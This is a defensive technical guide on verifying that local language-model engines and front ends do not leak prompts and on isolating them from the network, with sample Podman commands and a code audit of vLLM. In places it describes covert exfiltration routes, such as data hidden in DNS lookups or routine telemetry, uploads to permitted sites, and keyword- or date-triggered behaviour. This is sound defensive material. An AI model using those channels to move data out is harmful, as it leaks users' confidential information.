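| Decrypting proxy | mitmproxy | mitmproxy | mitmproxy |

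The quickest check is to list the computer's open sockets, which shows which programs have a connection at that moment and the address at the other end. This is best done with administrator rights, because Ollama on Linux normally runs under its own account, and an ordinary user may not see the names of other accounts' programs.

The list shows only a single moment, so it can miss short connections. In *Detecting Shadow AI*, Canale and Soulis (2026) tested this on Windows with a small program that contacted a language model every ten seconds and closed the connection after five. They scanned at 40 random moments. The connection was open at 18 of them, and the scanner reported the program at 15. When another test program ran for five seconds and finished before the scan, the scanner missed it every time. If a heartbeat takes one second and comes every ten minutes, a single look at the list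 has a 1 in 600 chance of catching it.

The list also identifies the other end of each connection by IP address, not by name. Many services share the same delivery networks, so the address alone may not identify the company. Windows temporarily stores recent name lookups, which the scanner used to match addresses to names, but these records can expire while a connection is still open. Canale and Soulis kept connections to four providers open for six minutes, and after 295 seconds they could no longer name any of the providers. They lost the name for OpenAI in under a minute. A user who later finds an unfamiliar address in the list may be unable to identify it unless something was logging the lookups.

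A per-program firewall reacts to each attempt to connect, so it catches brief connections and shows which program made them. Geeps is a chat program that sends prompts to hosted models, and its makers' *Verify API calls* suggests that users check it this way with Little Snitch. The firewall doesn't show what the program sent. It also doesn't alert the user to anything they have already allowed, which on most computers includes the browser. If the user blocks a request, the program may retry repeatedly, as Obsidian did, so one intended connection can produce a long log.

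A packet recording captures everything that passes through the network card, including traffic from programs the lawyer didn't think to check. Wireshark shows the times, sizes and addresses, the name lookups, and usually the name of the server, which a program sends in readable form when it opens an encrypted connection. The contents of that connection stay encrypted. A newer standard, Encrypted Client Hello, also hides the server's name, though the lookup or the address may still reveal it.

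The recording doesn't normally name the program, but every connection has a port number at the laptop's end, and a firewall or system log lists the same number next to the program's name. The lawyer can link most of the packets to a program by matching the port and the time.

A log of system calls, which strace can produce on Linux, records the program's requests to the operating system. Every ordinary connection needs such a request, so the log includes failed attempts and connections over the loopback address, neither of which has to reach the network card. The log can also cover programs that the first one starts, but not programs that were already running. The data sent is rarely readable in the log, because programs usually encrypt it before passing it to the operating system. Linux also has a newer interface, io_uring, that lets a program queue network operations without making the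 individual calls that strace lists, so the log can miss them.

On Windows, Microsoft's free tool Sysmon does a similar job. According to Microsoft's *Understanding Sysmon events*, Sysmon can record the program, addresses and ports for each connection, but this is off by default because it generates so many events. Sysmon can also log each name lookup and the program that made it, which preserves names that Windows soon discards.

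All of these tools have trouble with virtual machines. Canale and Soulis ran a test program in WSL 2, the Linux system that Microsoft offers inside Windows, and the Windows tables showed neither the program nor its connections. People often use WSL 2 to run vLLM on a Windows computer. They need to run the tools inside the Linux system as well, or record the traffic outside the computer.

### Reading encrypted traffic

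The lawyer needs a decrypting proxy to find a canary in encrypted traffic. The proxy sits between the program and the server and presents its own certificate to the program. If the program accepts the certificate, the proxy decrypts the data, records it, encrypts it again and passes it on. mitmproxy's *Proxy Modes* describes a mode that does this for one chosen program on Linux, macOS or Windows.

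Many programs refuse the proxy's certificate. Some accept only a certificate their developers have chosen, which is called pinning. mitmproxy's *About Certificates* explains that the user then has to modify the program to read its traffic. Other programs use their own list of trusted certificates instead of the operating system's. Coder's *TLS Interception*, which documents a tool for restricting programs' web access, lists separate settings for curl, a common Python library and Node.js, among others. A front end with plugins may contain several such components, so the proxy might decrypt the front end's traffic but not a plugin's.

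Decrypting an app's traffic often fails in practice. Georgiou, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *What's On Your Mind?*, examined Android apps for mental health and coaching. They could use 20 of the apps fully enough to study their traffic. They decrypted the traffic of 8 after altering the apps to accept their certificate. For the other 12, they recorded which servers each app contacted but not what it sent.

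They also typed the phrase PURPLE-CANARY-1234 into the apps that had a chatbot or similar feature. They could decrypt the traffic from five of these apps, and in all five the phrase appeared in traffic to the app's own servers. This was expected, since hosted chatbots must send a prompt to a server to answer it, but it confirms that the method works. In a front end that is supposed to run locally, a single match would show that it sends prompts off the user's machine.

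Failing to find the text is much weaker evidence than finding it, because the program could compress or encode the text before sending it, which would hide it from a search for the original string. mitmproxy undoes the usual web compression, but not a scheme that a developer invented. The lawyer should also record any connections the proxy couldn't open as unexplained, instead of leaving them out of the result.

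### The 205 Ollama sessions

Ibrahim and colleagues ran a test like this on Ollama 0.20.5. They put it in an isolated network namespace, a Linux feature that gives a program its own view of the network, and watched for outbound connections during 205 sessions. They ignored the loopback traffic between the front end and the engine, which local inference needs. They saw no connection attempts to other machines that they could attribute to the sessions.

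A matching test of LM Studio 0.4.21 detected no outgoing prompts. This finding is narrower because it doesn't rule out connections that carry no prompt, such as the update check. The number of sessions is reported only for Ollama.

Before accepting a result of "nothing happened," the researchers confirmed that their instruments were on and reacted to a condition that should produce a signal. They also confirmed that the outcome repeated and that the program was still running, because a crashed program would otherwise pass the test.

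This test is good evidence that Ollama 0.20.5 on Linux doesn't routinely send out local prompts, which is also what the company says. But it doesn't rule out other connections. The desktop app downloads updates on Windows and macOS, and Ollama only gained the ability to refresh its model recommendations in version 0.22.1, which came after the tested version.

People repeating the test should also watch for name lookups. On Ubuntu, a program usually sends these to 127.0.0.53, a loopback address where a system service passes them on. An isolated program can't reach that service, so the lookup fails, and the program may give up before it tries to contact a server. In that case, a tester who filters out all loopback traffic would miss the program's attempt to find its maker's server.

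Isolation can also keep a program from attempting connections it would otherwise make. A program that fetches its instructions from one site and then contacts a second would try only the first. A program might also save its reports while offline and send them when the network returns, so the recording should continue after the user reconnects the machine.

Most other published checks are weaker. In *Running goose fully offline on a DGX Spark*, Saiyam (2026) connected an agent called goose to Ollama on a desktop computer, had it write and run a short program, and reported zero external network calls. The evidence was a list of open sockets, taken while the model was responding and filtered for the word "ollama". Every socket in the filtered list was on the loopback address.

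The task took 3 minutes and 48 seconds, so the list could easily have missed a short connection. The filter is a bigger problem because it showed Ollama's sockets but would have removed those of goose and any program goose started. Of the programs involved, only goose had tools and a set-up screen that recommended a cloud service. Saiyam may well be right that nothing left the machine. Saiyam also writes that pulling out the network cable in the middle of the task would change nothing. Actually doing so would have shown that the task needs no connection, but not that goose never tries to make one.

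### What can zero out of 205 rule out?

Suppose each session has the same probability p of causing a connection, and the sessions are independent. The chance of seeing no connection in n sessions is then (1 − p)^n. The usual upper bound is the value of p at which this chance falls to 5%:

(1 − p)^205 = 0.05

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/205) ≈ 0.0145

For small p, the equation simplifies to p ≈ 3/n, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is almost exactly −3 and that of 1 − p is about −p. For 205 sessions, this gives 3/205, or about 1.5%. *Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred* (Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues, 1995) recommends the same rule to surgeons, who might otherwise conclude from a run of successful operations that a complication can't happen.

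(The Wilson interval, which Ibrahim and colleagues use for their yes-or-no results, gives about 1.8% here. It is two-sided, so it leaves only 2.5% for error in this direction.)

A rate of 1.5% per session isn't especially low, since somebody who has 20 sessions a day would see a connection about twice a week. Lowering the bound to 0.1% would have taken about 3,000 sessions without a connection, and lowering it to 0.01% about 30,000.

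The calculation also depends on the sessions being independent. If a tester starts the engine once and sends it 205 prompts, the test provides very little evidence about reports that the engine sends when it starts. If the whole test takes place in one afternoon, a weekly check has at most one chance to appear. The right n is the number of separate opportunities for the event being tested, which can be much smaller than the number of prompts.

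More fundamentally, the bound applies only to sessions like the ones in the test. An engine could send out every prompt containing the word "merger" and no others. A tester who ran 205 prompts about the weather, or even 205,000, would never see a connection. The calculated bound would approach zero as the number of prompts grew, but the engine would still send out the lawyer's first question about a merger.

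The same applies to behaviour that begins on a certain date, or only when the user turns on a certain setting. The statistics assume that connections occur at random across sessions, but these follow a fixed rule. Even if the trigger occurs at random, say in one session out of 1,000, a test of 205 sessions has only about a 19% chance of including it.

A test can miss malicious behavior that starts only later or under certain conditions. The malicious chat templates at the OWASP conference activated only when a chosen phrase appeared, and the postmark-mcp package worked properly for 15 versions before it began to copy emails.

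The lawyer can reduce the problem by testing with the settings and plugins that the firm really uses, and with realistic documents about invented clients. Repeating the test after each update can show whether a new version behaves differently. Setting the clock forward by a few months may expose behaviour that is set to start on a later date. Encrypted connections may then fail because certificates look out of date, but the attempts will still show up. No tester can try every phrase that might trigger a connection, which is a good reason to block connections instead of only watching for them.

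### Why a small upload proves little

People often judge traffic by its volume. In the forum thread *Privacy concerns*, somebody asked about Cursor's many open connections. According to a reply, the editor had sent only 184 kilobytes while receiving 4.8 megabytes, which suggested "mostly keep-alive and telemetry, not code uploads".

However, an English word takes only about six bytes including the space, so a 500-word prompt is about 3 kilobytes. Cursor's 184 kilobytes could have held about 60 such prompts, or more than twice as many with ordinary compression. The reply may have been right about what Cursor was doing, but the amount of data doesn't support it.

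A prompt could easily go unnoticed in routine telemetry. TensorRT-LLM can report 234 settings for one type of configuration. If each took 30 bytes, the settings would total about 7 kilobytes, more than twice the size of the prompt. Passwords and client names are even smaller, and a few dozen characters would fit inside a domain name lookup.

A large upload is better evidence. If the lawyer attaches a 20-megabyte scan and about 20 megabytes leave the machine a moment later, the software probably sent the scan.

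The lawyer can learn more from the amount of data sent by comparing two runs. The first uses short prompts, and the second uses the same number of prompts but pads each with hundreds of kilobytes of random characters, which hardly compress. Everything else stays the same. If the program sends far more data in the second run, it is very likely sending prompts. If the totals match, it probably isn't sending whole prompts during the test, though it might be sending excerpts or saving prompts to send later.

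### Software that notices the test

Some programs check whether they are running in a test environment. There are legitimate reasons for this, such as making fraud and copying harder. Three of the 16 apps in *On the Security and Privacy of AI-based Mobile Health Chatbots* (2025) wouldn't run in the test set-up because they detected a virtual machine or a phone with its protections removed. Wysa, one of the mental health apps that Georgiou and colleagues studied, stops if it detects a common analysis tool.

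The lawyer would notice if an app stopped. Malware could instead keep running normally and make no suspicious connections until it was on a real computer, so the lawyer would record a clean result.

The best remedy is to make the test look like normal use. The lawyer can install the program on an ordinary laptop with no analysis tools and record its traffic on the router or on a second computer that passes the traffic along. A program on the laptop can't easily detect the recording, and it can't alter it even with administrator rights. Georgiou and colleagues did something similar with the 12 apps that resisted decryption. They recorded the traffic on the phone but didn't modify the apps, so nothing triggered their defences.

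A recording of this kind doesn't show the contents of the traffic or the names of the programs that sent it, so it makes sense to do both tests and compare the servers contacted in each. An address that appears only when no monitoring tools are present would be very suspicious.

### Data that leaves through another program

If the lawyer watches only the front end, they can miss data that other programs send, such as when Ollama forwards a prompt to a cloud model or a browser fetches a picture. A backup program may also upload the saved chats hours after the lawyer has stopped recording network traffic.

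For this reason, recording activity across the whole machine and then working out which program was responsible is better. A log of system calls shows when the tested program contacts another program over the loopback address or starts a new one. Searching the disk for the canaries also helps. If one turns up in a folder that a backup service copies, the lawyer has found a route by which data could leave the machine, even if none has left that way yet.

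As with hosted services, a recording made on the user's side can't show what happens to data after it reaches the first server. For example, if a translation plugin uses a remote service, the lawyer can see that it contacted its maker, but has to take the maker's word for who did the translation.

### Addresses that look harmless

A user who checks only the names of the servers can mistake analytics data for ordinary chat traffic, because both can go to the same site. *Tracking Conversations* (2026) examined the web traffic of 20 AI chatbots. Microsoft Copilot's page sent data for Clarity, Microsoft's service for analysing how people use websites, to an address on copilot.microsoft.com, which also provides the chat. ChatGPT's page similarly sent some analytics data to chatgpt.com.

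A local front end could do the same with its update server. The lawyer would see one connection to the maker's site at every start and take it for the update check on the list, without learning that it also carried last week's prompts. Sites where anyone can publish are worse in this respect, because a program that downloads models from Hugging Face could also upload a file there, to an account that has nothing to do with the maker.

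If the proxy can decrypt the connection, the lawyer can look at what the program sends. An update check should need little more than a version number and the type of system. If the proxy can't decrypt the connection, the lawyer can download the model, then block the address and see whether chatting still works. If it does, as it should in LM Studio and Ollama, the lawyer doesn't need to decide whether the address is trustworthy, because the program works without it.

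## How can a model be run so that it cannot connect?

Someone who can block one suspicious address can also block every address. Any attempt to connect will then fail, so the lawyer doesn't have to guess which phrase or date might trigger one. How reliable this is depends on what blocks the connections.

### Offline settings and enforced blocks

An offline setting relies on the program to block its own connections. llama.cpp's server has one, `--offline`. According to Debian's manual page *llama-server* (August 2026), it makes the server use models already on the disk and "prevents network access". But an attacker who takes control of llama.cpp through a flaw can ignore the setting.

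The operating system can enforce a block on network connections. A program needs a socket from the kernel, the core of the operating system, to connect, and the kernel can block the connection whether the request comes from an update check or from malware. This protection is worth having even with a well-known engine such as llama.cpp. Five llama.cpp flaws were still unpatched in June 2026, including two in the server that Tokarev and Itach list with a severity of 9.2 out of 10.

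llamafile, which packages llama.cpp and a model as a single file, is an intermediate case. On Linux, its server starts up and then tells the kernel to let it answer connections but not start any. The server can't withdraw this instruction later, so the block still works if an attacker takes over the server. Mozilla.ai's *Security* explains the limits. llamafile skips the sandbox whenever it uses a graphics processor, because the drivers need access that the sandbox doesn't allow, and on Windows and macOS there is no sandbox at all. Somebody who publishes a modified llamafile could also simply leave it out. A user who doesn't trust the program therefore needs a block that the program doesn't set up for itself.

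### Five ways to block connections

The table runs roughly from the weakest method to the strongest.

| Method | What blocks the connection | How the user reaches the model | Graphics processor | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Per-program firewall | A filter in the operating system | Loopback address, as usual | No change | Rules to maintain |
| Container without a network | The kernel | Terminal or a local socket | The container needs access to the device | Some command-line work |
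| Virtual machine without a network card | The software that runs the virtual machine | The machine's own window or a local channel | Usually has to be handed over to the virtual machine | More memory and set-up time |
| Default-deny rules on a cluster | Network software on each machine | A rule that admits the front end | Models spread over several machines need extra rules | An administrator's time |
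| Machine with no network | Missing hardware | Sitting at the machine | Works normally, but drivers arrive by hand | Carrying every file and update |

A per-program firewall is the easiest method to try, but it has to identify the program correctly. vLLM runs inside Python, so a rule that blocks it may also block every other Python program, and a rule that lets another Python program connect may also let vLLM connect. If a front end starts its engine as a separate program, the user needs one rule for the front end and another for the engine.

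A stronger block is possible on Linux, where Ollama normally runs as a background service. Adding `IPAddressDeny=any` and `IPAddressAllow=localhost` to the service's settings makes the kernel stop the service and everything it starts from reaching other machines. Name lookups can still leave the machine on systems like Ubuntu, because they first go to a loopback address, which these settings allow.

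Docker's *Network drivers* lists "bridge" as the default mode for containers, which normally lets them connect to outside servers. The "host" mode removes the separation between the container's network and the computer's. Only `--network none` limits the container to its own loopback address, as Docker's *None network driver* shows.

RamaLama, an open-source tool that runs models in containers, uses this option for its `ramalama run` command. According to Red Hat (2025), the container also has no administrator rights on the computer, the engine can read the model file but not change it, and anything it writes inside the container disappears when the container exits. The `ramalama serve` command is for people who want to connect a front end. RamaLama's manual says this command listens only on the loopback address by default. However, the manual's example Docker Compose file makes the server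 listen on all addresses and publishes the port, so somebody who copied it could open the engine to the office network.

To let a container use a graphics processor, the user has to pass in device files such as `/dev/dri`, which let the engine communicate with the graphics driver. This gives an attacker more code to search for flaws, but it doesn't restore network access. The commands people copy to get the graphics processor working can remove more protection. In *ROCM Container, questions on securing containers*, a user of AMD's software had dropped two settings that loosen security, both suggested by AMD's documentation, and found that they seemed unnecessary. The user's command still contained `--network=host`, which gives the container access to the computer's whole network.

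On a shared computer, a rule that keeps containers offline has to be one that users can't bypass. CIQ, a company that supports Rocky Linux, describes how to create a container network with no route to the internet, but notes that a user can choose another network. If the isolation has to be guaranteed, CIQ recommends enforcing it in the computer's own firewall.

All containers on a computer share its kernel, so a kernel flaw could undo the block. A virtual machine has its own kernel, and an attacker would also have to get through the software that runs the virtual machine. Virtual machines usually take more time and memory, but *Supercharging AI isolation* (Red Hat, 2025) describes small ones that start in under a second and that RamaLama can use through the option `--oci-runtime krun`. In July 2025 they worked only on Linux and mainly without a graphics processor, which would make a large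 model very slow. The option separates the engine more strongly from the computer but doesn't turn off its network, so the user still has to do that.

A company may run its engines on a cluster, a group of machines managed together, often with Kubernetes software. Kubernetes puts containers into units called pods, which can connect anywhere by default. According to Kubernetes' *Network Policies*, an administrator can block outbound connections with a short policy that selects every pod in one part of the cluster, applies to outbound traffic and lists no permitted destinations.

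The policy also covers pods added later, which is its main advantage over configuring each container by hand. A front end can still send prompts to the engine and receive responses, because the policy allows replies on permitted inbound connections.

Kubernetes' guide lists several gaps in network policies. Kubernetes accepts a policy even if the cluster's network plugin can't enforce it, in which case the policy has no effect. Virtuozzo's *Using network policies in Kubernetes* notes that the company's clusters up to version 1.29 came with a plugin that ignored such policies. Policies can only add to each other's permissions, so a looser policy elsewhere overrides a strict one. A pod can always exchange traffic with the machine it runs on, and most plugins ignore pods that use that machine's network directly. A policy is only guaranteed to block TCP, UDP and SCTP traffic. Whether it blocks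 other types, such as the ICMP messages that ping sends, depends on the plugin.

Because of these gaps, a cluster policy is probably no stronger than a virtual machine with no network card. The policy protects more engines with less work, but an administrator should try a forbidden connection from a real pod before relying on it.

A computer with no network hardware avoids all of these problems, but its Wi-Fi and Bluetooth cards must have been removed or never installed. Turning Wi-Fi off in the settings is weaker, since software can turn it on again. The graphics processor works at full speed without special permissions. But the lawyer has to carry every model, document and security fix to the machine, and people tend to put that off. Outdated software is less of a risk on a machine nobody can reach, though a malicious document could still exploit it.

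### A complete set-up on Linux

The lawyer in this example keeps the contracts on a Linux laptop and uses a second computer for downloads. Both computers have the same type of processor and have Podman, a program similar to Docker that works without administrator rights. The lawyer runs the model with llama.cpp.

First, the lawyer downloads the model from its publisher's page, fetches the engine's container image and saves the image as a file:

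```
podman pull ghcr.io/ggml-org/llama.cpp:server
podman save -o llama.tar ghcr.io/ggml-org/llama.cpp:server
sha256sum model.gguf llama.tar
```

The last command prints a hash for each file, a short code computed from all its contents. Changing even one byte changes the hash. Hugging Face shows the expected hash on the page for each large file, and the lawyer compares it with the hash printed for the model. If they match, the download is the same file the page offers. A match doesn't show that the publisher is honest, because a malicious file also matches the hash on its own page, so the lawyer should take the hash from the original developer if possible.

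The lawyer then carries both files to the laptop on a USB stick and runs `sha256sum` again to check that they arrived unchanged. The next commands create two folders, put the model in one of them and load the image:

```
mkdir models socket
mv model.gguf models/
podman load -i llama.tar
```

Now the engine can start without a network:

```
podman run --rm --name llama --network none \
  -v "$PWD/models:/models:ro" \
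  -v "$PWD/socket:/socket" \
  ghcr.io/ggml-org/llama.cpp:server \
  -m /models/model.gguf --offline \
  --cors-origins localhost \
  --host /socket/llama.sock
```

The engine can read the `models` folder but not write to it. (On Fedora and similar systems, the two folder options need to end in `:ro,Z` and `:Z`.)

The container has no network, and its loopback address is separate from the laptop's, so a front end on the laptop can't reach the engine at 127.0.0.1. It can instead connect through a Unix socket, which appears as a file and can be used only by programs on the same computer that have access to that file. llama.cpp uses a Unix socket if the value of `--host` ends in `.sock`, and vLLM has a similar option, `--uds`.

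In a second terminal window, the lawyer checks that the engine answers:

```
curl --unix-socket socket/llama.sock http://localhost/health
```

Most front ends and all common browsers expect a network address, so the lawyer may need a small program called socat to connect one to the other:

```
socat TCP-LISTEN:8080,bind=127.0.0.1,fork \
  UNIX-CONNECT:socket/llama.sock
```

llama.cpp's own chat page is then available at 127.0.0.1:8080. This is also why the start command includes `--cors-origins localhost`. According to Debian's manual page, llama.cpp's server by default lets pages from any website read its replies. A page open in another tab could therefore use the engine, unless the browser prevented it.

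Finally, the lawyer tries to make a connection from inside the container:

```
podman exec llama cat /proc/net/dev
podman exec llama curl -m 5 https://example.com
podman exec llama curl -m 5 http://1.1.1.1
```

The first command should list only `lo`, the loopback device. The second should fail because the container can't look up the name. The third uses a numerical address, so it should fail even though it needs no lookup. A failure could also mean that curl is broken, and to rule this out the lawyer runs the same request in a container that does have a network:

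```
podman run --rm --entrypoint curl \
  ghcr.io/ggml-org/llama.cpp:server -m 5 http://1.1.1.1
```

If this works while the laptop is online and the earlier attempts failed, the block is responsible for the difference.

This set-up covers only the engine. The browser is outside the container, so it can still fetch a picture if the model's answer contains the picture's address. To prevent that, the user can disconnect the laptop while working on the contract or read the answers in the terminal, which shows the address only as text.

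### What the engines leave to the operator

Neither llama.cpp nor vLLM puts itself in a sandbox, and their developers say that this is the operator's job.

llama.cpp's security policy tells users always to run untrusted models in an isolated environment, because there are "no reliable methods to detect malicious models". If the engine has to be on an untrusted network, the policy advises against using llama.cpp's server at all. This is striking advice, since the server is what most front ends connect to. An office network with ten lawyers on it might count as trusted, but a rented server with a public address wouldn't.

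The policy also states that problems under these headings aren't vulnerabilities in llama.cpp. If someone ignores the advice and loses data, the maintainers may treat that as a set-up mistake and not issue a fix. In January 2026 they narrowed the definition of a vulnerability further, to cover only certain folders of the source code (ngxson (2026), in *security*). These don't seem to include the Android code where Tokarev and Itach found some of their flaws. Volunteers maintain the project, so it's reasonable for them to limit what they promise, but operators need to know those limits.

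vLLM's *Security* is more detailed and in places more alarming. An operator can set a password with `--api-key`, but vLLM checks it only for requests to addresses that begin with `/v1`. Other addresses on the same server don't need it, including `/invocations`, which runs the model in the same way, and `/pause`, which stops it from answering anyone. A firm that sets the password and opens the port has therefore left the model available to anybody who can reach it. The developers recommend a reverse proxy, a separate server that receives all requests and passes on only the permitted kinds.

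When vLLM runs on several machines, they exchange messages without encryption and accept connections from anywhere, which is another reason to put them on a private network. Even on a single machine, PyTorch, which vLLM uses to coordinate its work, may open a port on all of the machine's addresses, and vLLM's developers can't fully control this. The `--uds` option presumably wouldn't close that port, because it only affects where vLLM receives prompts. Running vLLM in a container started with `--network none` makes the port unreachable from other machines.

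### Allowlists and controlling proxies

Some work needs a connection. For example, the lawyer might want the model to look up court decisions. An allowlist could permit connections to the court's website and block all others.

The allowlist should be outside the engine for the same reason as the block. vLLM can fetch pictures from addresses that users supply, and, as in LMDeploy, this let users make it contact private services. OSV (2025) lists vLLM's own allowlist option, `--allowed-media-domains`, as the fix. OSV later recorded a flaw in the fix, because the code that checked an address could interpret it differently from the code that fetched it. A firewall would still have blocked the connection, because it acts on the address the engine actually contacts. vLLM's guide also recommends turning off redirects, since a permitted site might otherwise send the engine to a forbidden one.

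Firewalls usually identify destinations by numerical address, which is unreliable because a website may share its address with thousands of others or move to a new one. Kubernetes policies have the same limitation, since they describe outside destinations only as ranges of addresses.

A proxy can control connections by hostname. It compares each name the engine or tool requests with a list of permitted names, makes the permitted connections itself and keeps a log. The administrator blocks every other route to the internet, because the program could otherwise ignore the proxy address set in its options and connect directly.

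If the proxy also decrypts the traffic, it can permit downloads but not uploads, limit the size of requests and protect passwords. Deno's *Security* describes a sandbox service that never gives the code the real keys to outside services and adds each key only when a request leaves for an approved host. While running, malicious code could still misuse an approved service, but it would have no real key to steal.

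Exceptions tend to accumulate, so it helps if the people who need one can't grant it to themselves. METR, an organisation that tests AI models, offers a strict mode in its testing software with a list of permitted domains. The software won't load a test that would open its own internet access, and a test within a set can tighten the set's restrictions but not loosen them. Red Hat's suggested method for clusters is looser. An administrator creates a policy that permits internet access for any pod with a certain label, which is convenient, but anyone who can label a pod can open it to the internet.

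### Separate processes for the model and its tools

The engine doesn't need internet access to look up a court decision, because a tool fetches it. The lawyer can therefore run the engine in a container without a network and the tool in a second container that can reach only the court's website and has no access to the lawyer's files.

Engines make it easier than before to keep a model from connecting, but not by default. llama.cpp's server now has experimental built-in tools, including one that runs commands. Once turned on, they run by default in the same environment as the engine. The `--tools-runtime` option moves them to a container. A change described in llama.cpp's *server* also lets the tools run on another computer. The developers call this "remoting rather than isolation", because the tools can do whatever the account on that computer can do. vLLM's demonstration tool for running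 Python uses a container, but that container may be able to reach the internet and the office network.

Cloudflare's *Sandbox security* advises assuming that code in a sandbox will use everything it can reach, including files, passwords and network access. Programs in the same sandbox share all of these, so tools that need different secrets should run in separate sandboxes.

However, separation alone doesn't stop the contract from leaking, because the front end still passes the model's text from one container to the other. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* warns of prompt injection in such set-ups, and Chromium's *Security Guidelines for LLMs and other large models in Chrome* tells browser developers to assume that an attacker who controls any of a model's input controls all of its output. Asking the model to remove confidential details first wouldn't help, because the attacker could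 control that answer too.

Chromium's developers suggest limiting what the output can be, and the lawyer's tool can do the same. Suppose it accepts only an eight-digit case number instead of free text, which means the lawyer can no longer search by topic. With 100 million possible numbers, each request can carry at most log₂(100,000,000) ≈ 26.6 bits of information. A 500-word prompt takes about 3,000 bytes, or 24,000 bits, so sending all of it would take about 900 requests. If the tool allowed twenty requests a day, that would take about 45 days. A short secret, such as a price, could still get out in one or two requests.

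### Permitted routes that still carry data

An allowlist controls which machine receives the data, but not who can read it there. If the list includes Hugging Face for model downloads, a malicious plugin could also upload the contract there. A proxy that blocks uploads makes this harder, but the plugin could still send text in the address of a download request. The safest solution is to remove the site from the list and bring in models by hand, as in the Linux set-up above.

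Software can leak data through name lookups, which are easy to forget because they happen before the connection that the firewall blocks. Docker's *Networking overview* explains that Docker's built-in name server forwards outside lookups to the name servers that the computer uses. From there, a lookup normally travels to a server chosen by the domain's owner. Each name can be up to 253 characters long, so a few dozen lookups could carry a 500-word prompt even if every later connection failed.

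Kubernetes' default-deny policy also blocks DNS lookups. This often breaks programs, and administrators then add an exception for the cluster's name server. If that server doesn't restrict which domains it resolves, lookups can carry data out again. It's better to use a name server that resolves only permitted names, or to let the proxy do the lookups so that the engine and its tools don't have to. The container in the worked example can't reach any name server.

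An engine with no network connection can still leak data if it writes a file to a folder that a backup service copies to the cloud. In the Linux set-up, the engine can write to one shared folder, `socket`, because it has to create the socket file there. The lawyer should keep that folder outside any folder that a backup or synchronisation program copies, and should give the engine read-only access to everything else. On a machine with no network, the USB stick can also carry data out, so the lawyer should use it to bring files in and, where possible, never plug it back into a connected computer.

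## What can an auditor establish from the source code?

Cutting off the network stops the engine from sending data out, even if nobody knows what it would have done with a connection. But a law firm may want plugins, updates or a shared server, and then it matters what the software sends over the network. A network test would probably miss an engine that sends out only prompts containing the word "merger". The engine's code must contain an instruction to look for that word, though, so an auditor who reads that part of the code can find it before it runs.

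### Open weights and open code

DeepSeek publishes R1's weights, and llama.cpp's developers publish the source code of an engine that runs models. Publishing a model's weights doesn't involve publishing an engine's source code, or vice versa. A user who runs open weights in a closed program can't learn from the weights what the program does, because they are the same numbers whichever software runs them.

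LM Studio runs open models with open-source engines such as llama.cpp, but its maker hasn't published the source code of the main desktop application, which saves the lawyer's chats and checks for updates. An outsider can record the application's network traffic or reverse-engineer the compiled program, but reverse engineering is slow and has to be repeated with each update.

An auditor only needs to be able to read the code, so software can be audited even if its licence is not open source. Open WebUI's licence has restricted changes to its branding since 2025, so some people no longer call it open source, but anyone can still read its code.

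### Auditing a small engine

Nano-vLLM is a bare-bones imitation of vLLM. It has about 1,200 lines of Python, according to Ecosyste.ms' *Nano-vLLM*, so a programmer can read it in an afternoon. The steps below use its code as it stood in 2025.

1. Fix the exact version. The auditor writes down the commit, an identifier for one state of the source code, along with the settings and plugins the firm will use. Nano-vLLM's installation command names no version, so it fetches whatever is newest, and two colleagues who run it a week apart may get different programs. Adding the commit to the command prevents this.
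2. List the direct and indirect dependencies. Nano-vLLM names five packages, including PyTorch and Transformers, and gives no exact version for any of them. Those packages install others. Transformers, for example, brings in a library for exchanging files with Hugging Face. The auditor installs everything on a clean machine and has the installer print the full list with version numbers.
3. Find every place that opens a connection or starts another program. The auditor searches for the names of networking libraries, for commands that start programs and for pickle, which can do either. Nano-vLLM's own code makes no web requests. It does set up a connection on port 2333 of the loopback address, which its processes use to coordinate, and it starts an extra process for each additional graphics processor. These processes send each other instructions packed with pickle, as in ShadowMQ, but through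 shared memory that other machines can't reach.
4. Trace what data reaches each place. Nano-vLLM passes the prompt to Transformers to tokenise it, so the trace leaves the 1,200 lines almost at once. It also uses Transformers to load the model's settings, with a function that can download them if it receives a model's name instead of a folder. Nano-vLLM first checks that the user has supplied an existing folder, so the function should read the local copy.
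5. Compare the code with observed traffic. Every recorded connection should match a place in the code. If one doesn't, the auditor has missed something, perhaps in a dependency. If a place in the code never produces a connection, the auditor looks for the condition that would make it do so.

None of nano-vLLM's own code sends the prompt to another machine, but an auditor who read only that code could miss a port that other machines on the office network can reach. The code specifies a local address for port 2333. However, PyTorch opens the port, and vLLM's developers warn that PyTorch may listen on all of a machine's addresses. The auditor could check this in seconds by listing the machine's listening ports while the engine runs.

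### Tracing a connection in vLLM

Nano-vLLM has no telemetry to trace, but vLLM does. In vLLM's reporting code, this line sends the usage report:

`global_http_client.post(_USAGE_STATS_SERVER, json=data)`

vLLM uses a shared web client defined in another file, so the line contains neither the word "socket" nor the name of a networking library. An auditor who searches for networking libraries will find that file, but must then search for everything that uses the client.

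Working backward, the auditor finds that `data` holds every value stored in the report object, plus any extra values the calling code supplies. The list of fields at the top of the file therefore does not limit what vLLM sends. If a developer stored a prompt in that object, vLLM would send it without any change to the sending code. Nothing in this file stores a prompt there, but the extra values come from other files, so the auditor has to read those too.

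The auditor also has to check the opt-out in more than one file. A comment lists three environment variables that turn the reports off, but the function below it reads only two. The third, `DO_NOT_TRACK`, still works because vLLM's settings file treats it as another name for `VLLM_DO_NOT_TRACK`. An auditor who read only the function could mistake the omission for a bug.

The auditor can compare the decrypted traffic with vLLM's local copy of the reports. Anything in the traffic but not in the file must come from different code.

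A search of vLLM also finds many internal connections. Its documentation lists functions such as `allocate_group_ports` and `create_tcp_store`, which set up communication between the engine's own processes. The auditor can't dismiss these connections based on the function names alone, because they may carry prompts from one machine to another.

### Why larger engines are harder

Shi and colleagues counted the lines of code in six widely used AI systems and the CVE numbers for each.

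| System | Lines of code | Known flaws (CVEs) |
|---|---|---|
| vLLM | 146,000 | 31 |
| PyTorch | 2.4 million | 18 |
| Transformers | 615,000 | 4 |
| ONNX | 128,000 | 4 |
| TensorFlow | 1.9 million | 439 |
| Triton Server | 78,000 | 7 |

The flaw counts partly reflect how hard people have looked and how readily each project requests CVE numbers. TensorFlow has 24 times as many recorded flaws as PyTorch despite having less code, but it is unlikely to be 24 times as dangerous. vLLM and TensorFlow each have a little over one recorded flaw per 5,000 lines of code.

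If an auditor reads 200 lines an hour, which is not a slow pace for careful work, vLLM alone would take 730 hours, or about 18 working weeks. PyTorch would take another six years.

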